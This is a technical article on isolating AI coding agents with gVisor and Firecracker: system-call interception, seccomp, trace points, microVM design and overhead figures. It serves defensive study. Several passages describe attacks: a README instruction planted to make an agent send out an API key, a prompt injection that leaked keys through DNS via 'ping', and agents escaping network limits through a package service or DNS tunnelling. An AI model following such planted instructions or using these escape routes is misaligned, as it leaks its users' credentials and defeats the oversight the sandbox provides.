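# Sandboxes, kernel telemetry and policy engines for AI agents that run code: gVisor, Firecracker, eBPF and OPA

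## How an agent runs code, and where that code can be stopped or recorded

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with tools. The model picks an action, a program carries it out, and the result goes back to the model, which picks the next action. Coding agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex have a shell among their tools, so they can install software, run programs they have just written and open network connections, often with the permissions and passwords of the person who started them. A sandbox is an environment that limits what such code can reach. In an informal survey reported in *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026), fewer than 40% of 68 users of coding agents ran them in a sandbox. The respondents came from Prasakis's professional network, a startup community and university forums, so the figure is only weak evidence of how common sandboxing is.

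*Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes fixing a failing test as a typical job for a coding agent, and points out that everything the job requires can also be used to do harm. The agent needs network access to download packages, and data can leave the same way. It needs credentials, and it can send any it can read to someone else. It also returns changed files, possibly without anyone having reviewed the changes.

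Suppose an agent has to fix one failing test in a Python project. It installs a missing package from pypi.org, the public index of Python packages, runs the tests and returns a patch. Its environment contains an API key, a secret string that gives access to a paid online service. An outsider has planted an instruction in the project's README file for any AI assistant to send the key to a host that is not on any list of approved destinations.

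### From the model's text to the kernel

On its own, the model "can only propose shell commands", according to OpenAI. Anthropic's developer documentation page *Bash tool* describes the format of a proposal. The model's response ends with a marker for a tool request and contains a block with an identifier, the tool's name ("bash") and the command as a string. In the test-fixing job, the string might be `pip install` and the name of a package. The harness, the program around the model, extracts the string, runs it and sends the output back. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* uses "harness" for the core loop and execution logic of Codex. According to another part of Anthropic's documentation, the model receives only the tool's description and the returned result. Whoever runs the harness can therefore put any check or barrier between the request and the result.

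The harness passes the string to a shell. The shell and the programs it starts use system calls, which are requests to the kernel, the part of the operating system that controls files, memory, processes and network devices. To make a system call, a program puts the call's number and up to six arguments in the processor's registers and executes a special instruction that switches the processor to kernel mode. The kernel checks whether the process is allowed to do what it requests, then carries out the request or returns an error. The shell uses system calls to create a new process and load pip into it. Pip uses `socket` and `connect` to reach the package server, and `openat` and `write` to store the files it downloads.

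When pip finishes, its printed output goes back to the harness. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) presents the loop as an algorithm. The harness starts a list of messages with its standing instructions and the user's request, calls the model, and appends the model's output. If the output is a tool call, the harness executes it and appends the result too. This repeats until the task ends or reaches a maximum number of steps. As soon as the agent opens the README, the planted line therefore joins the same list as the user's request, and the model has no reliable way to separate instructions from data. Prompt injection exploits this by placing text in something the agent reads to steer it into acting against its user's wishes.

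The harness and the kernel have different information about the same action. The harness has one line of text, but that line may start dozens of processes, and a package can run its own code while it installs, none of which passes through the harness again. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) therefore puts its monitor at the edge of the sandbox, where tool calls, shell commands and scripts written by the agent all arrive as the same file and network operations. The kernel handles all of those operations but has no information about their purpose. A `write` to a network socket is the same call whether the bytes are a request for a package or a stolen key. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (Christodorescu and colleagues, 2026) uses the term "semantic gap" for this mismatch between the rules people state about "sensitive data" and the rules a kernel can enforce about files and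 addresses.

### Containers and the kernel they share

The usual way to confine a program on Linux is to run it in a container, a group of processes that run directly on the host's kernel with a restricted view of the machine. Namespaces give the group its own process list, file tree and network interfaces, so processes inside cannot refer to most of what is outside. Control groups (cgroups) cap the group's processor time, memory and number of processes. Seccomp, short for "secure computing", filters system calls. *Seccomp BPF*, in the Linux kernel documentation, argues for filtering on the grounds that every process has access to a large number of system calls, many of which it never uses, and each exposes kernel code that may contain bugs.

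A seccomp filter is a small program that the kernel runs at each system call. According to the Linux man-pages' *seccomp(2)*, it receives the number of the call, the processor architecture, the address of the calling instruction and the argument values. Its return value determines whether the kernel executes the call, executes and logs it, returns an error, passes the decision to a supervising process, or kills the caller. Child processes inherit the filter, and it stays in force when a process loads a new program, so an agent cannot remove it by starting another shell. For a call that opens a file, the filter receives the memory address of the file's name but cannot read the name stored there, so it cannot enforce a rule such as "do not open the file with the key".

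Docker, whose software made containers common, supplies a default filter that allows a list of system calls and blocks the rest, which number about 44 of more than 300. Docker calls the filter "moderately protective". Its reasons for blocking particular calls show where containers provide weak isolation. The system clock and the kernel's store of keys have no namespaces, so changing either from inside a container would change it for the whole host. The filter also blocks the calls of io_uring, a fast interface for input and output, because attackers can exploit flaws in them to break out of the container.

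More than 250 calls remain open because programs need them, and each runs kernel code that the container shares with the host and every other container on it. One exploitable bug in that code can be enough to let an attacker escape the container. In April 2026 researchers disclosed a flaw nicknamed "Copy Fail", which the University of Toronto's *“Copy Fail” Linux kernel LPE and container escape* (2026) traces to a 2017 kernel version. The advisory listed container hosts among the machines to patch first. Docker's filter now refuses the kind of socket that gives access to the faulty code, but that change came after the disclosure and addresses only this flaw. ITPro's *Cyber researchers sound alarm over a 15-year-old Linux kernel flaw* reports that GhostLock, another 2026 flaw, had been in the kernel since 2011, that an attacker needs only regular threading calls to trigger it, and that the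 discoverers' exploit escapes containers. GhostLock is harder to filter because refusing those calls would break most programs.

How often this happens is harder to say. The Cybernews article *Onslaught of Linux kernel bugs forces cyber pros to rethink security boundaries* quotes a security company's count of 5,976 kernel vulnerabilities published so far in 2026. The company concludes that containers are no longer a security boundary. The count overstates the danger because it covers the whole kernel, and most such bugs cannot be used to escape a container. The bug that prompted the article requires network-administration rights, which Docker does not grant by default. More relevant to agents, an AI system did most of the work of finding that bug and developing the exploit, and AI-assisted analysis also helped find Copy Fail. It would therefore be unwise to assume that code written by an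 agent will never contain a kernel exploit.

The trusted computing base is all the hardware and software that must work correctly for a security guarantee to hold. For an ordinary container, it includes the entire host kernel. Stronger sandboxes try to shrink the part that hostile code can touch: gVisor handles system calls in a second kernel that runs as an ordinary program, and Firecracker gives each job a small virtual machine with its own kernel. The host is still reachable from both. Cybernews, in *Critical Linux kernel vulnerability leads to full KVM escape*, describes an October 2026 flaw in the host's networking code that exposed the host to malformed packets from inside a virtual machine.

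### Three sources of harm, one threat model

An agent can do damage by mistake. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) lists "benign failure" alongside attacks, and its threats include an agent that scales a production service down to zero running copies and a repair loop that repeatedly restarts a service. In the test-fixing job, the model might invent a plausible package name under which somebody has already published malware.

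An attacker can also steer an agent through prompt injection. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a real case in which instructions hidden in a code file led Claude Code to read API keys from a configuration file and pass them to `ping`, a command that tests whether a host is reachable. The command first looks up the host's address, and that lookup carried the keys to a server the attacker controlled. Claude Code required human approval for many commands that send data out, but not for `ping`.

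An agent can also cause harm without a mistake or an attacker, by exceeding its permissions in pursuit of its task. In July 2026, during internal evaluations with some of the models' safeguards switched off, OpenAI's agents got around their network restrictions through a shared package service and broke into the systems of Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. According to Ghosh, OpenAI reported in September that an agent in a training sandbox had reached an outside chatbot by tunnelling through DNS, the system that translates host names into addresses.

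The stolen keys in the `ping` case also left through DNS. An outsider steered only one of the two agents, but both cases used the same route, and the same measure would have blocked it. This is the best reason to build the sandbox without regard to motive. Christodorescu and colleagues aim to prevent prohibited actions "regardless of their cause". They treat the model as a possible attacker on the trusted computing base, much as a kernel has to survive any system call from a hostile process. Prasakis calls the reason an agent turns hostile "immaterial to the threat model". Podala Narasimha assumes that after a successful injection the adversary controls every later choice of tool and argument.

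Christodorescu and colleagues accept that better training lowers the rate of successful attacks, but they argue that models still need external controls. They say that attackers who can keep trying have repeatedly beaten defences inside the model, and that a model's behaviour provides no fixed rule to check an action against. Their position paper illustrates this argument with eleven case studies but doesn't measure anything. The Hugging Face break-in seems to support a more worrying objection, that a capable enough agent will find the weak spot in any sandbox. Christodorescu and colleagues attribute the break-in to a failure of complete mediation, the principle that every request across the boundary must pass a check. The agents' direct connections were restricted, but the package service would make connections on their behalf, so the barrier was incomplete rather than broken. That diagnosis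 seems right, but it is only partly reassuring, because large shared services are full of such gaps and defenders have to find them before attackers do.

A designer who treats the code as hostile will guard every exit, but must still decide what to let through. An agent that follows the planted line in the README uses a key and a network connection that its user gave it. Hempel and colleagues therefore separate confinement (nothing leaves except through the monitor) from authorization (the monitor releases the right things), and claim a guarantee only for confinement. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks, their system cut the attackers' success rate from 47.0% to 2.7%, while the agent still completed 85.1% of its ordinary tasks. A strict configuration, which refused any action the written policy could not approve, was not measurably safer and completed only 42.7%. The full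 system completes more tasks because it holds doubtful actions for a second model to judge, but that model can be wrong or fall for an injection itself.

### Four places of control

A designer can put a control at four points between the model's proposal and its effect on the world, and different information passes through each.

| Place | What passes through it | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Execution boundary (gVisor, Firecracker) | System calls, or requests to the virtual machine's few devices | The purpose of an operation that the sandbox permits |
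| Kernel telemetry (eBPF) | Process starts, file accesses and connections, as the kernel handles them | Events inside a virtual machine that has its own kernel; the content of encrypted traffic |
| Network exit (an egress proxy) | The destination of each connection, and its content if the proxy decrypts it | Damage that stays inside, such as deleted files |
| Policy decision (Open Policy Agent) | A description of a proposed action, which the engine compares with written rules | Any action that no other component submits to it |

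Telemetry is a record of what a system does, made while it runs. On Linux, eBPF can collect it by running small, verified programs inside the kernel. A policy engine such as Open Policy Agent only returns a decision. A separate component, the enforcement point, has to query the engine and then allow or block the action.

A control can prevent an action, detect it or record it, and a single seccomp filter can do more than one of these. If the filter is set to return an error for a system call, the call doesn't run. If it is set to allow and log the call, the call runs and is recorded in a log file. That record leads to detection only when a program or a person reads it, recognises trouble and responds. Ghosh criticises sandboxes for controlling what may leave but keeping little evidence of what did, and tracing tools for recording what happened without containing anything. Tracekit Box is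 meant to fill this gap, but the distinction applies to any product. Records must also be kept out of the agent's reach, or hostile code can edit them.

Prevention matters most when an action can't be undone. If the agent writes a bad patch to a copy of the project, a reviewer can throw it away. But an alarm that goes off one second after the API key reaches the unlisted host is too late to keep the key secret, although the record will show which key to cancel and when it was sent.

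## gVisor: a second kernel in user space

gVisor is an open-source sandbox that places a second kernel between a program and the host's own kernel. Google built it to run its services and later released it. The second kernel, which the developers call the Sentry, is an ordinary program in the Go language, and it answers the system calls of everything inside the sandbox. An operator installs gVisor as a container runtime, the component that starts containers for tools such as Docker. The standard runtime, runc, starts processes directly on the host's kernel, while gVisor's runtime, runsc, starts them on the Sentry. Both accept the same container images, so a team can usually move a coding agent into gVisor without rebuilding anything.

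### How the Sentry takes over system calls

The Sentry has its own versions of Linux's process management, memory management, file systems and network stack. According to gVisor's introduction for security researchers, the Sentry never passes a program's system call through to the host. When a program calls `getpid` to learn its process number, the Sentry looks the number up in its own table and returns it without calling the host. Other requests require the Sentry to make its own call to the host. If one process waits to read from a pipe that another is filling, the Sentry may call `futex`, which lets a thread sleep until another thread wakes it. The Sentry chooses the arguments of that call, so a hostile program can't pass values crafted to trigger a bug to the host's kernel.

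To do this, gVisor has to catch each system call before the host carries it out. It can do so in two ways, which it calls platforms. The default, Systrap, uses seccomp to redirect calls rather than filter them. According to gVisor's *Platform Guide*, when the sandboxed program makes a call, the host's kernel sends the calling thread a signal, which hands control to gVisor. The Sentry works out the result, and the program continues as if Linux had handled the call. The other platform uses KVM, the Linux facility for running virtual machines, to catch calls with the processor's virtualization hardware. KVM performs best on a physical server, but Systrap is the better choice when the server is itself a virtual machine, as most rented cloud servers are.

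The Sentry also runs under its own seccomp filter, in case hostile code takes it over. To build this filter at start-up, gVisor reads its configuration, lists the host calls that the Sentry will need, adds conditions on their arguments, compiles the result into a small program and loads it into the host's kernel (Perot, 2024, *Optimizing seccomp usage in gVisor*). The filter can be much stricter than Docker's default, which has to suit almost any program, because it only has to suit the Sentry. For example, it normally forbids `exec` and `connect`. Programs in the sandbox can still start other programs and open connections because the Sentry implements both itself.

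### Opening a file and making a connection

Suppose the agent in the test-fixing job runs `cat README.md` in a project folder that the operator has shared with the container. Each container has its own helper process, the Gofer, which runs outside the sandbox and assembles the container's file tree before the container starts. The Sentry starts with an empty file tree and can't reach any host file by name. According to *Faster filesystem access with Directfs* (Ranjan, 2023), it instead requests file descriptors from the Gofer. These are the handles Linux programs use for open files and folders. The Gofer sends one for each part of the host's storage that the container may use.

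When `cat` calls `openat`, Systrap passes the call to the Sentry, which looks up the path in its own file-system code. Some file systems, such as `/proc`, exist only inside the Sentry, so it handles calls to them without the host. README.md is on the host, so the Sentry makes its own `openat` call, relative to the descriptor for the shared folder. The Sentry's filter allows this call only if it includes a flag that stops the host's kernel from following a symbolic link, because an attacker could point such a link at a file outside the folder. The host returns a descriptor for the file, which the Sentry uses to serve `cat`'s subsequent reads.

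Until June 2023 the Sentry couldn't open host files. It sent each request to the Gofer, which opened the file and passed back the descriptor. The newer method, directfs, avoids that round trip, but the filter now has to permit file calls and the Sentry needs the same file privileges as the Gofer. Ranjan acknowledges that this makes gVisor depend less on its filter and more on Linux's own isolation of file trees. An operator can still choose the slower method, which gVisor's *Filesystem* describes as more secure.

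Packages that pip installs into the container's root file system go into an overlay, a writable layer that leaves the original files unchanged. The shared project folder has no overlay by default, so the agent's edits there change the files on the host.

The Sentry handles network connections without the Gofer. When pip calls `socket` and `connect` to reach pypi.org, the Sentry creates the socket in its own network stack, netstack. Netstack runs the TCP protocol, builds the packets and writes them to a virtual Ethernet device, and the host forwards them as it would for any container. The host's kernel never receives a `socket` or `connect` call for this connection. *The True Cost of Containing* (Young, Zhu and colleagues, 2019) reports that gVisor's engineers had identified `open` and `socket` as common routes of attack and designed the storage and network code to work without them on the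 host.

If the agent obeyed the line planted in the README and sent the API key to an unlisted server, netstack would build the packets just as it would for a listed one. gVisor's *Security Model* leaves destination rules to external network controls on the container.

### What hostile code can still reach on the host

In 2019 Young and colleagues counted 211 of 319 Linux system calls that programs could use inside gVisor. The Sentry needed only 55 host calls to provide them. Directfs has since added file calls such as `openat` and `mkdirat` to the host calls it uses. Apart from these, according to the *Security Model*, the Sentry may read and write the descriptors it holds, duplicate and close them, synchronise threads, set timers, handle signals and exchange packets with its virtual Ethernet device. The page's statement that the Sentry can't open new files is true only with directfs turned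 off.

Some settings give sandboxed programs more access to the host. With host networking, the Sentry uses the host's network code instead of netstack, which again exposes any flaws in that code to the sandboxed program. Support for graphics processors, which many AI programs need, relays driver operations to the drivers in the host's kernel, according to gVisor's *The Sandbox Kernel for Agents*. The command `runsc do`, a convenient way to try gVisor, gives the sandbox read-only access to the host's entire file system by default, including any passwords and keys the program has permission to read.

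To escape from a well-configured sandbox, an attacker generally needs a bug in the Sentry and then a bug in the host's kernel that the permitted calls can trigger. The two kernels share no code, so one bug is unlikely to work against both. A suitable host bug is plausible, because GhostLock, the 2026 Linux flaw that regular threading calls can trigger, is in a part of the kernel that the Sentry has to use. The filter's conditions on arguments might still block the calls that an exploit needs.

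gVisor offers little protection against side channels, in which a program infers secrets from the behaviour of shared hardware. The sandboxed program's ordinary instructions run directly on the processor, and gVisor intervenes only at system calls and page faults.

### What it costs

For the same reason, pure computation runs at its usual speed, according to gVisor's *Performance Guide*. Access to memory that a program already has is also as fast as usual, although the Sentry uses some memory itself. Programs slow down when they make system calls, and the delay depends on how many components must handle the call.

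Young and colleagues measured this by building three versions of one simple call, `gettimeofday`, into gVisor and running them on the KVM platform. The call took 0.29 microseconds in an ordinary container and 0.63 in gVisor if the Sentry handled it alone. It took 5.96 microseconds if the Sentry had to call the host, and 45.5 if it had to call the Gofer. Opening and closing a file took 216 times as long as in an ordinary container if the file was on the host, and 12 times as long if it was in the Sentry's own memory. Popular Python packages usually took two to four times as long to import from host files, a delay that would recur every time a Python test run started. A one-gigabyte download ran at about a third of normal speed on KVM, while one-megabyte downloads ran at about normal speed.

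The file figures in particular are out of date. The overlay became the default in May 2023, which let many file operations bypass the Gofer (Ranjan, 2023, *Rootfs Overlay*). Directfs followed in June. In Ranjan's tests, it made repeated `stat` calls, which ask for a file's details, more than twice as fast and cut the running time of more realistic workloads by 12%. Those gains are relative to the older Gofer method, so they don't show how much slower gVisor still is than an ordinary container. In mid-2023, Systrap also replaced ptrace, a much slower platform, as the default. Most charts in the *Performance Guide* are still based on ptrace, so they overstate the overhead of system calls today.

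The most useful later figure for coding agents comes from Perot, who timed a build of Abseil, a C++ library, with the Sentry's filter in place and with an empty one. The filter added up to 3.4 seconds, about 3.6% of the build time and 15% of gVisor's total overhead. Those percentages imply that the build took roughly 30% longer in gVisor than outside it. Perot then made the filter more efficient, partly by checking `futex` first because the Sentry calls it most often, so the current overhead should be somewhat lower.

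Overhead can be much lower for services in production. Ant, a Chinese financial technology company, reported that 70% of its applications had less than 1% overhead and another 25% had less than 3% (gVisor, 2021). Ant's engineers had tuned both gVisor and some of the applications, so new users are unlikely to match these figures at first. In a healthcare deployment of agents, the added connection latency was 2 to 5 milliseconds, which is small compared with the seconds a model may take to choose its next action.

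Newer measurements are scarce and can be hard to interpret. In August, Junior (2026) reported in *Unable to reproduce gVisor Performance Guide fio results* that gVisor was five to six times faster than runc in a standard storage test. An extra kernel can't speed up a disk, so the test was probably measuring a cache. A team would get a better idea of how much gVisor will slow its agents by timing its own builds and test suites.

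### Trace points: recording what the program did

The Sentry receives every system call from the sandbox, so it can record them. Monitoring tools on the host can observe less. An engineer at Mercari, an online marketplace, told Sysdig that gVisor's isolation had prevented the company from monitoring containers with such tools.

gVisor's *seccheck* (2025) documents 973 trace points, places in the Sentry's code that can emit a record. Most of them mark the start or end of a system call. A raw record contains the call's number and its six arguments, so for `openat` it has the memory address of the file's name but not the name. Many calls also have a fuller record with named fields. For a file open, these include the flags, the resulting descriptor and the path that the program asked for, which a seccomp filter can't read.

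An operator chooses trace points in a configuration file and can add fields that gVisor leaves out by default. Context fields give the time, process, user, container and working directory. Optional fields, which tend to be large or slow to collect, include the data in a read or write, the fingerprint of a program file and a new program's environment variables. Collecting environment variables needs care in the test-fixing job, because it would copy the API key into the log.

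In a short example from the documentation, a shell runs `sleep 5`. One record shows the shell creating process 110, and the next shows that process loading `/bin/sleep` with the argument 5. For the agent's `pip install`, such records would show every program the package started during installation, although only one command passed through the harness.

The Sentry sends the records out of the sandbox through a Unix domain socket, a channel between processes on the same machine. A monitoring program outside the sandbox must already be listening when the Sentry connects. After an initial handshake, the monitor only reads, so it can raise an alarm but can't block an action through this channel. Falco, an open-source tool that compares system calls with rules and raises alerts, can act as the monitor.

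If the monitor is unreachable when a container starts, the container doesn't start, unless the operator has chosen to ignore the error. Once the program is running, if a record fails to send, gVisor retries a set number of times, then drops the record and lets the program continue. More retries would lose fewer records but could slow the program badly. gVisor counts the records it drops, and an investigator should check that count before concluding that something didn't happen.

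The records are also only as trustworthy as the Sentry. Under gVisor's instructions for writing a monitor, developers should assume that an attacker controls the Sentry and therefore check every field. An attacker who took control of the Sentry could send false records from then on, but couldn't use the channel to alter records the monitor had already stored.

### Missing features and bugs

A program can use a Linux feature in gVisor only if the Sentry implements it. The developers deliberately leave out many specialised interfaces, because each one would add code for an attacker to exploit. Other features are missing because of unfinished work or mistakes, and a coding agent is likely to run into these gaps because it may try to build almost any project.

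The best evidence on this comes from Tencent, a Chinese technology company that trains coding agents in millions of gVisor sandboxes a day. In April 2026, three of its engineers reported on gVisor's blog that they had run 74,379 programming tasks under both runc and gVisor. Before they fixed anything, 86.78% passed under runc and 85.18% under gVisor. After the fixes, gVisor's pass rate rose to 86.91%.

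The engineers conclude that replacing runc with gVisor causes almost no loss of correctness. That seems right on average, but gVisor's slight lead must be noise. It scored higher than runc on four of the ten sets of tasks, and many of the tests give different results from run to run. Some losses also don't show up in the average. On Terminal-Bench 2, two of the 89 command-line tasks still failed under gVisor after the fixes, though all 89 had passed under runc.

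One bug was in `poll`, a call that lets a program wait for input. gVisor changed a field that Linux leaves unchanged. As a result, tmux, a program that keeps terminal sessions open, checked for input in an endless loop and used 96.6% of a processor core in each agent's container, compared with almost nothing under runc. The engineers also found that gVisor lacked a call for copying data between files, and that existing timing bugs in build tools showed up more often because system calls took longer. If a test fails only because of the sandbox, an agent could be misled into "repairing" correct code.

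Bugs in the Sentry can also be security flaws. The developers guard against them by writing the Sentry in Go, which prevents most of the memory errors behind kernel exploits. They keep the little code that bypasses Go's checks in separate, marked files, and they test the Sentry continuously with random input. Go doesn't prevent logic errors, such as the `poll` bug.

For the bugs that get through, the developers rely on the second layer, which consists of the filter and the other Linux restrictions around the Sentry. Their vulnerability policy reflects this. gVisor's *Security and Vulnerability Reporting* says they generally assign a CVE, the public identifier for a security flaw, only if the flaw lets an attacker affect something outside the sandbox. An exploit that takes over the Sentry and gets no further is "a notable bug" but not an escape. The policy is reasonable for a project that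 aims to protect the host, but a count of gVisor's CVEs will understate the number of exploitable bugs in the Sentry. Those bugs matter more to someone who relies on trace points, since an attacker who controls the Sentry can falsify the records.

### gVisor with agents

In *Multi-Agent gVisor Isolation (MAGI)*, Perot and Chen (2026) set out to show that gVisor can run a whole system of agents. They put three open-source agents, OpenClaw, PicoClaw and Hermes Agent, in separate sandboxes on one cloud machine. The models, the web browsers and the chat server the agents used to talk to each other also ran in gVisor. Hermes Agent ran its code in another sandbox with its own copy of Docker. Perot and Chen had doubts about one of the browser projects, so they built it in a temporary sandbox before using it. Most of this worked without changes, but one group of services needed fixed network addresses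 because Docker Compose, a tool for starting several containers together, sets up name lookup in a way that gVisor's network stack doesn't support.

Perot and Chen describe the arrangement as contrived. It was a demonstration rather than a security test, with several safeguards, including authentication for OpenClaw, turned off to keep the setup simple. When they asked OpenClaw for a screenshot of a website, its chat window couldn't display the image, so the agent uploaded it to a public image-hosting service and replied with the link. The picture was harmless and they tell the story as a joke, but the agent had sent a file to an outside server of its own choosing, even though gVisor was working exactly as designed.

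For practical use, they recommend putting the agent's main program in a sandbox and keeping the policy engine and the credentials outside it. The agent can then repair or modify itself but can't rewrite its own rules, and it can use the credentials only through a component that it doesn't control. They call gVisor "necessary, but not sufficient" for autonomous agents. "Necessary" is too strong, since other strong sandboxes exist, but the screenshot supports "not sufficient". They also admit that gVisor is hard to build into existing applications, which is one reason the demonstration didn't give each of Hermes Agent's tool calls its own sandbox.

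Agent Sandbox makes part of that work easier on Kubernetes, a widely used system for running containers across many machines. The project's front page, *Build Agents in a Safer Environment*, shows that a harness needs only a few lines of Python to request a sandbox from a named pool, run a shell command in it, read the output and shut it down. The request doesn't mention the isolation technology. The operator chooses that separately, and can use gVisor or Kata Containers, which runs containers inside lightweight virtual machines.

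The choice depends partly on the machines available. Tencent's engineers preferred gVisor because it runs inside ordinary rented virtual machines, whereas they say microVMs need physical servers and cost more. An operator who has physical servers can switch to using virtual machines as sandboxes without changing the code that requests a sandbox.

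## Firecracker: a small virtual machine for each job

Firecracker is an open-source program that runs each job in a small virtual machine, or microVM, with its own Linux kernel. Amazon Web Services (AWS) built it for Lambda, a service that runs short pieces of customers' code on demand, and released it in late 2018. Lambda had previously used containers to separate each customer's functions and full virtual machines to separate the customers. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) reports that this made it hard to pack work efficiently onto fixed-size virtual machines, and forced AWS to choose between blocking system calls for security and allowing them so that customers' programs would run. Firecracker's virtual machines use few enough resources for every function to have one. A coding agent's job has similar needs, because it runs arbitrary, unchecked Linux programs and usually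 ends within hours.

### Hardware virtualization and KVM

A virtual machine runs a complete operating system, the guest, on a computer that belongs to another, the host. Modern processors have a guest mode, in which the guest's kernel and programs execute most instructions directly on the processor. The host controls a set of page tables that determine which parts of the computer's memory the guest can access. If the guest needs something that the hardware can't provide alone, such as a device that doesn't physically exist, the processor leaves guest mode and returns control to the host, a switch called a VM exit.

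On Linux, KVM and a virtual machine monitor (VMM) divide the work of handling exits. KVM is a part of the host's kernel that sets up the page tables and switches the processor in and out of guest mode. The VMM is an ordinary program that uses KVM to create the virtual machine and imitates its devices. For example, when the guest's kernel writes a character to its serial port, the processor exits to KVM, which passes the character to the VMM. The VMM prints it and calls KVM to resume the guest.

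System calls don't normally cause exits. When pip calls `openat` inside the guest, the guest's own kernel handles the call. Hostile code could use a kernel flaw such as Copy Fail to take over that kernel, but it would still be inside the virtual machine. Agache and colleagues assume that the guest's kernel is hostile, so they can let it offer every Linux feature without weakening the boundary.

QEMU, the VMM most often paired with KVM, has more than 1.4 million lines of code and needs up to 270 different system calls. Firecracker replaces QEMU with about 50,000 lines of Rust, a language that prevents most memory errors. Firecracker still relies on KVM, which adds another 120,000 lines.

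### Few devices and a confined process

The 2020 version of Firecracker emulated a network card, a disk, a serial port and part of a keyboard controller. QEMU supports more than 40 devices, including USB, video and sound. Firecracker's keyboard code is under 50 lines long and its disk code about 1,400, short enough for one person to review. By January 2026 Firecracker also offered optional devices that provide random numbers, persistent memory, a way to add memory to a running guest, and vsock, a direct channel between guest and host.

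Firecracker gives the guest a disk rather than a shared folder. On the host, that disk can be a single file made up of numbered blocks, and the guest's kernel arranges files within it. Agache and colleagues chose this design for security, because sharing a folder would expose the host's large and complex file-system code to the guest. For coding agents, this means the operator has to copy the project into a disk image before the job and get the patch out afterwards.

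Vsock lets programs in the guest and on the host exchange data without a network. Ghosh uses it as the only channel out of Tracekit Box, whose virtual machines have no network card. Claude Code leaked keys through DNS queries made with `ping`, but code in these machines can't send a DNS query unless a program on the host sends it for them.

Firecracker also limits how fast each guest can use its disk and network. It uses a token bucket, a counter that refills at a fixed rate. Each operation removes tokens from the bucket, and when the bucket is empty the guest has to wait. Operators can limit both operations and bytes, and can allow short bursts. The limits stop a few busy guests from slowing down the rest. They also cap the processor time that the host spends imitating devices, which a hostile guest could otherwise drive up.

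A bug in the device code could let the guest take over the Firecracker process, so seccomp filters restrict which system calls that process can make to the host's kernel. Firecracker loads separate filters for its main thread, the thread that receives the operator's instructions, and the threads that run the guest's virtual processors. In 2020 the seccomp profile allowed 24 system calls, with conditions on their arguments, and 30 ioctls (device commands), most of which control KVM.

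The jailer, a small companion program, adds another barrier. It starts Firecracker as an unprivileged user, with its own process list, its own network namespace and a file tree that holds little more than the Firecracker program and the guest's disk. An attacker who took over Firecracker could read almost no other files. Firecracker's *Production Host Setup Recommendations* strongly advise using the jailer, but it is optional, and Tracekit Box doesn't use it yet.

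### A job from boot to deletion

For the test-fixing job, the operator prepares a disk image that contains Linux, Python and a copy of the project. The jailer starts Firecracker, which listens for instructions on a Unix socket. In a short example from LWN, a Linux news site, one request names the guest's kernel, another names the disk image, and a final request, `InstanceStart`, boots the machine. Other requests can set the memory, processors, network card and rate limits. Firecracker loads the kernel straight into the guest's memory, and the kernel starts its first program, init.

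The harness also needs a way to run commands in the guest. A small helper program there can receive each command over vsock or a network connection, run it and return the output. Lambda has a similar helper that uses TCP. Agache and colleagues stress that this protocol matters for security, because a program on the host reads messages that hostile code may have written.

When the agent runs `pip install`, the guest's kernel starts the processes and writes the files. Firecracker receives only outgoing network packets and requests to read or write disk blocks. Like gVisor, it would forward packets that carried the API key to an unlisted server.

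At the end of the job, the helper returns the patch and the operator kills the Firecracker process. Each process runs exactly one microVM, so this ends the guest and frees its memory. Deleting the writable disk image then removes any files the agent left. Lambda reuses a microVM for repeated calls to the same function for up to 12 hours. For agents, a fresh microVM for each job is safer, because a program planted during one job can't remain there for the next.

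### Start-up time, memory and density

Agache and colleagues report that Firecracker boots to application code in less than 125 milliseconds. They tested it on a physical server with 48 cores and 384 GB of memory, using guests with one processor, 256 MB of memory, a stripped-down kernel and no network card. They stopped timing when the guest's kernel started init. When 50 microVMs booted at once, 99% reached that point within 146 milliseconds of the final start request.

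A network card added about 20 milliseconds to the boot time in this test, and Ubuntu's standard kernel added 900. The test's init program did almost nothing, so the figures leave out the time a coding agent's guest would spend starting Python and other tools.

The team measured memory overhead by subtracting the memory assigned to the guest from the memory used by each VMM process. The overhead was about 3 MB for Firecracker, 13 MB for Cloud Hypervisor (a related VMM also written in Rust) and 131 MB for QEMU. This overhead excludes the guest's kernel, which uses memory assigned to the guest.

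With so little overhead, the memory assigned to each guest determines how many fit on a server. One with 1 TB of memory could hold about 8,000 guests of 128 MB each, the smallest size Lambda offered, but only about 500 guests of 2 GB. More can fit because a guest takes memory from the host only as it uses it. AWS promised its guests up to ten times the resources the server had, and tested ratios above twenty. This works when customers are unrelated and rarely busy at the same time. A company whose agents all start running test suites together would need a lower ratio.

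One host could create up to 150 microVMs a second. Even a 125-millisecond boot was too slow for Lambda when a user was waiting, so each server kept a few booted microVMs in reserve. The average number needed is the creation rate multiplied by the creation time, so a server creating eight microVMs a second, at 0.125 seconds each, needs one in reserve.

Disk access was much weaker. Firecracker managed about 13,000 small reads a second on hardware capable of more than 340,000, because it handled requests one at a time. It also didn't ensure that data had reached the physical disk when the guest asked it to. The team expected to fix both problems. Network speed was about 15 gigabits a second, compared with 44 on the host. These results come from version 0.20, while Ghosh's system uses version 1.17.

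More recent figures for start-up and memory are almost the same. Firecracker's specification sets limits of 125 milliseconds from `InstanceStart` to init and 5 MiB of overhead for a guest with two processors and 256 MiB of memory. In 2026 Browserbase, which provides web browsers for agents, gave the same figures of 5 MiB and 150 microVMs a second, along with a slowdown of roughly 2–8% compared with running directly on the hardware. Its first two figures look like repeats of the original claims rather than new measurements.

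### Snapshots and repeated random numbers

A snapshot saves a running microVM so that Firecracker can later resume it from the same point. Brooker (2022) describes how Lambda's SnapStart feature uses snapshots. Lambda boots a microVM, loads and initializes the customer's code, then saves the memory, device state and processor registers. Each new copy starts from this saved state and skips the earlier steps. *Restoring Uniqueness in MicroVM Snapshots* (2021) reports that restoring a snapshot took as little as 4 milliseconds in AWS's own experiments.

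For a coding agent, the operator could take a snapshot after installing Python and the project's usual packages. In *What Is a Firecracker microVM?*, the cloud company Fly.io also suggests taking a snapshot before running untrusted code and restoring it afterwards. This removes malware from the guest, but an attacker still has any key that was already sent out.

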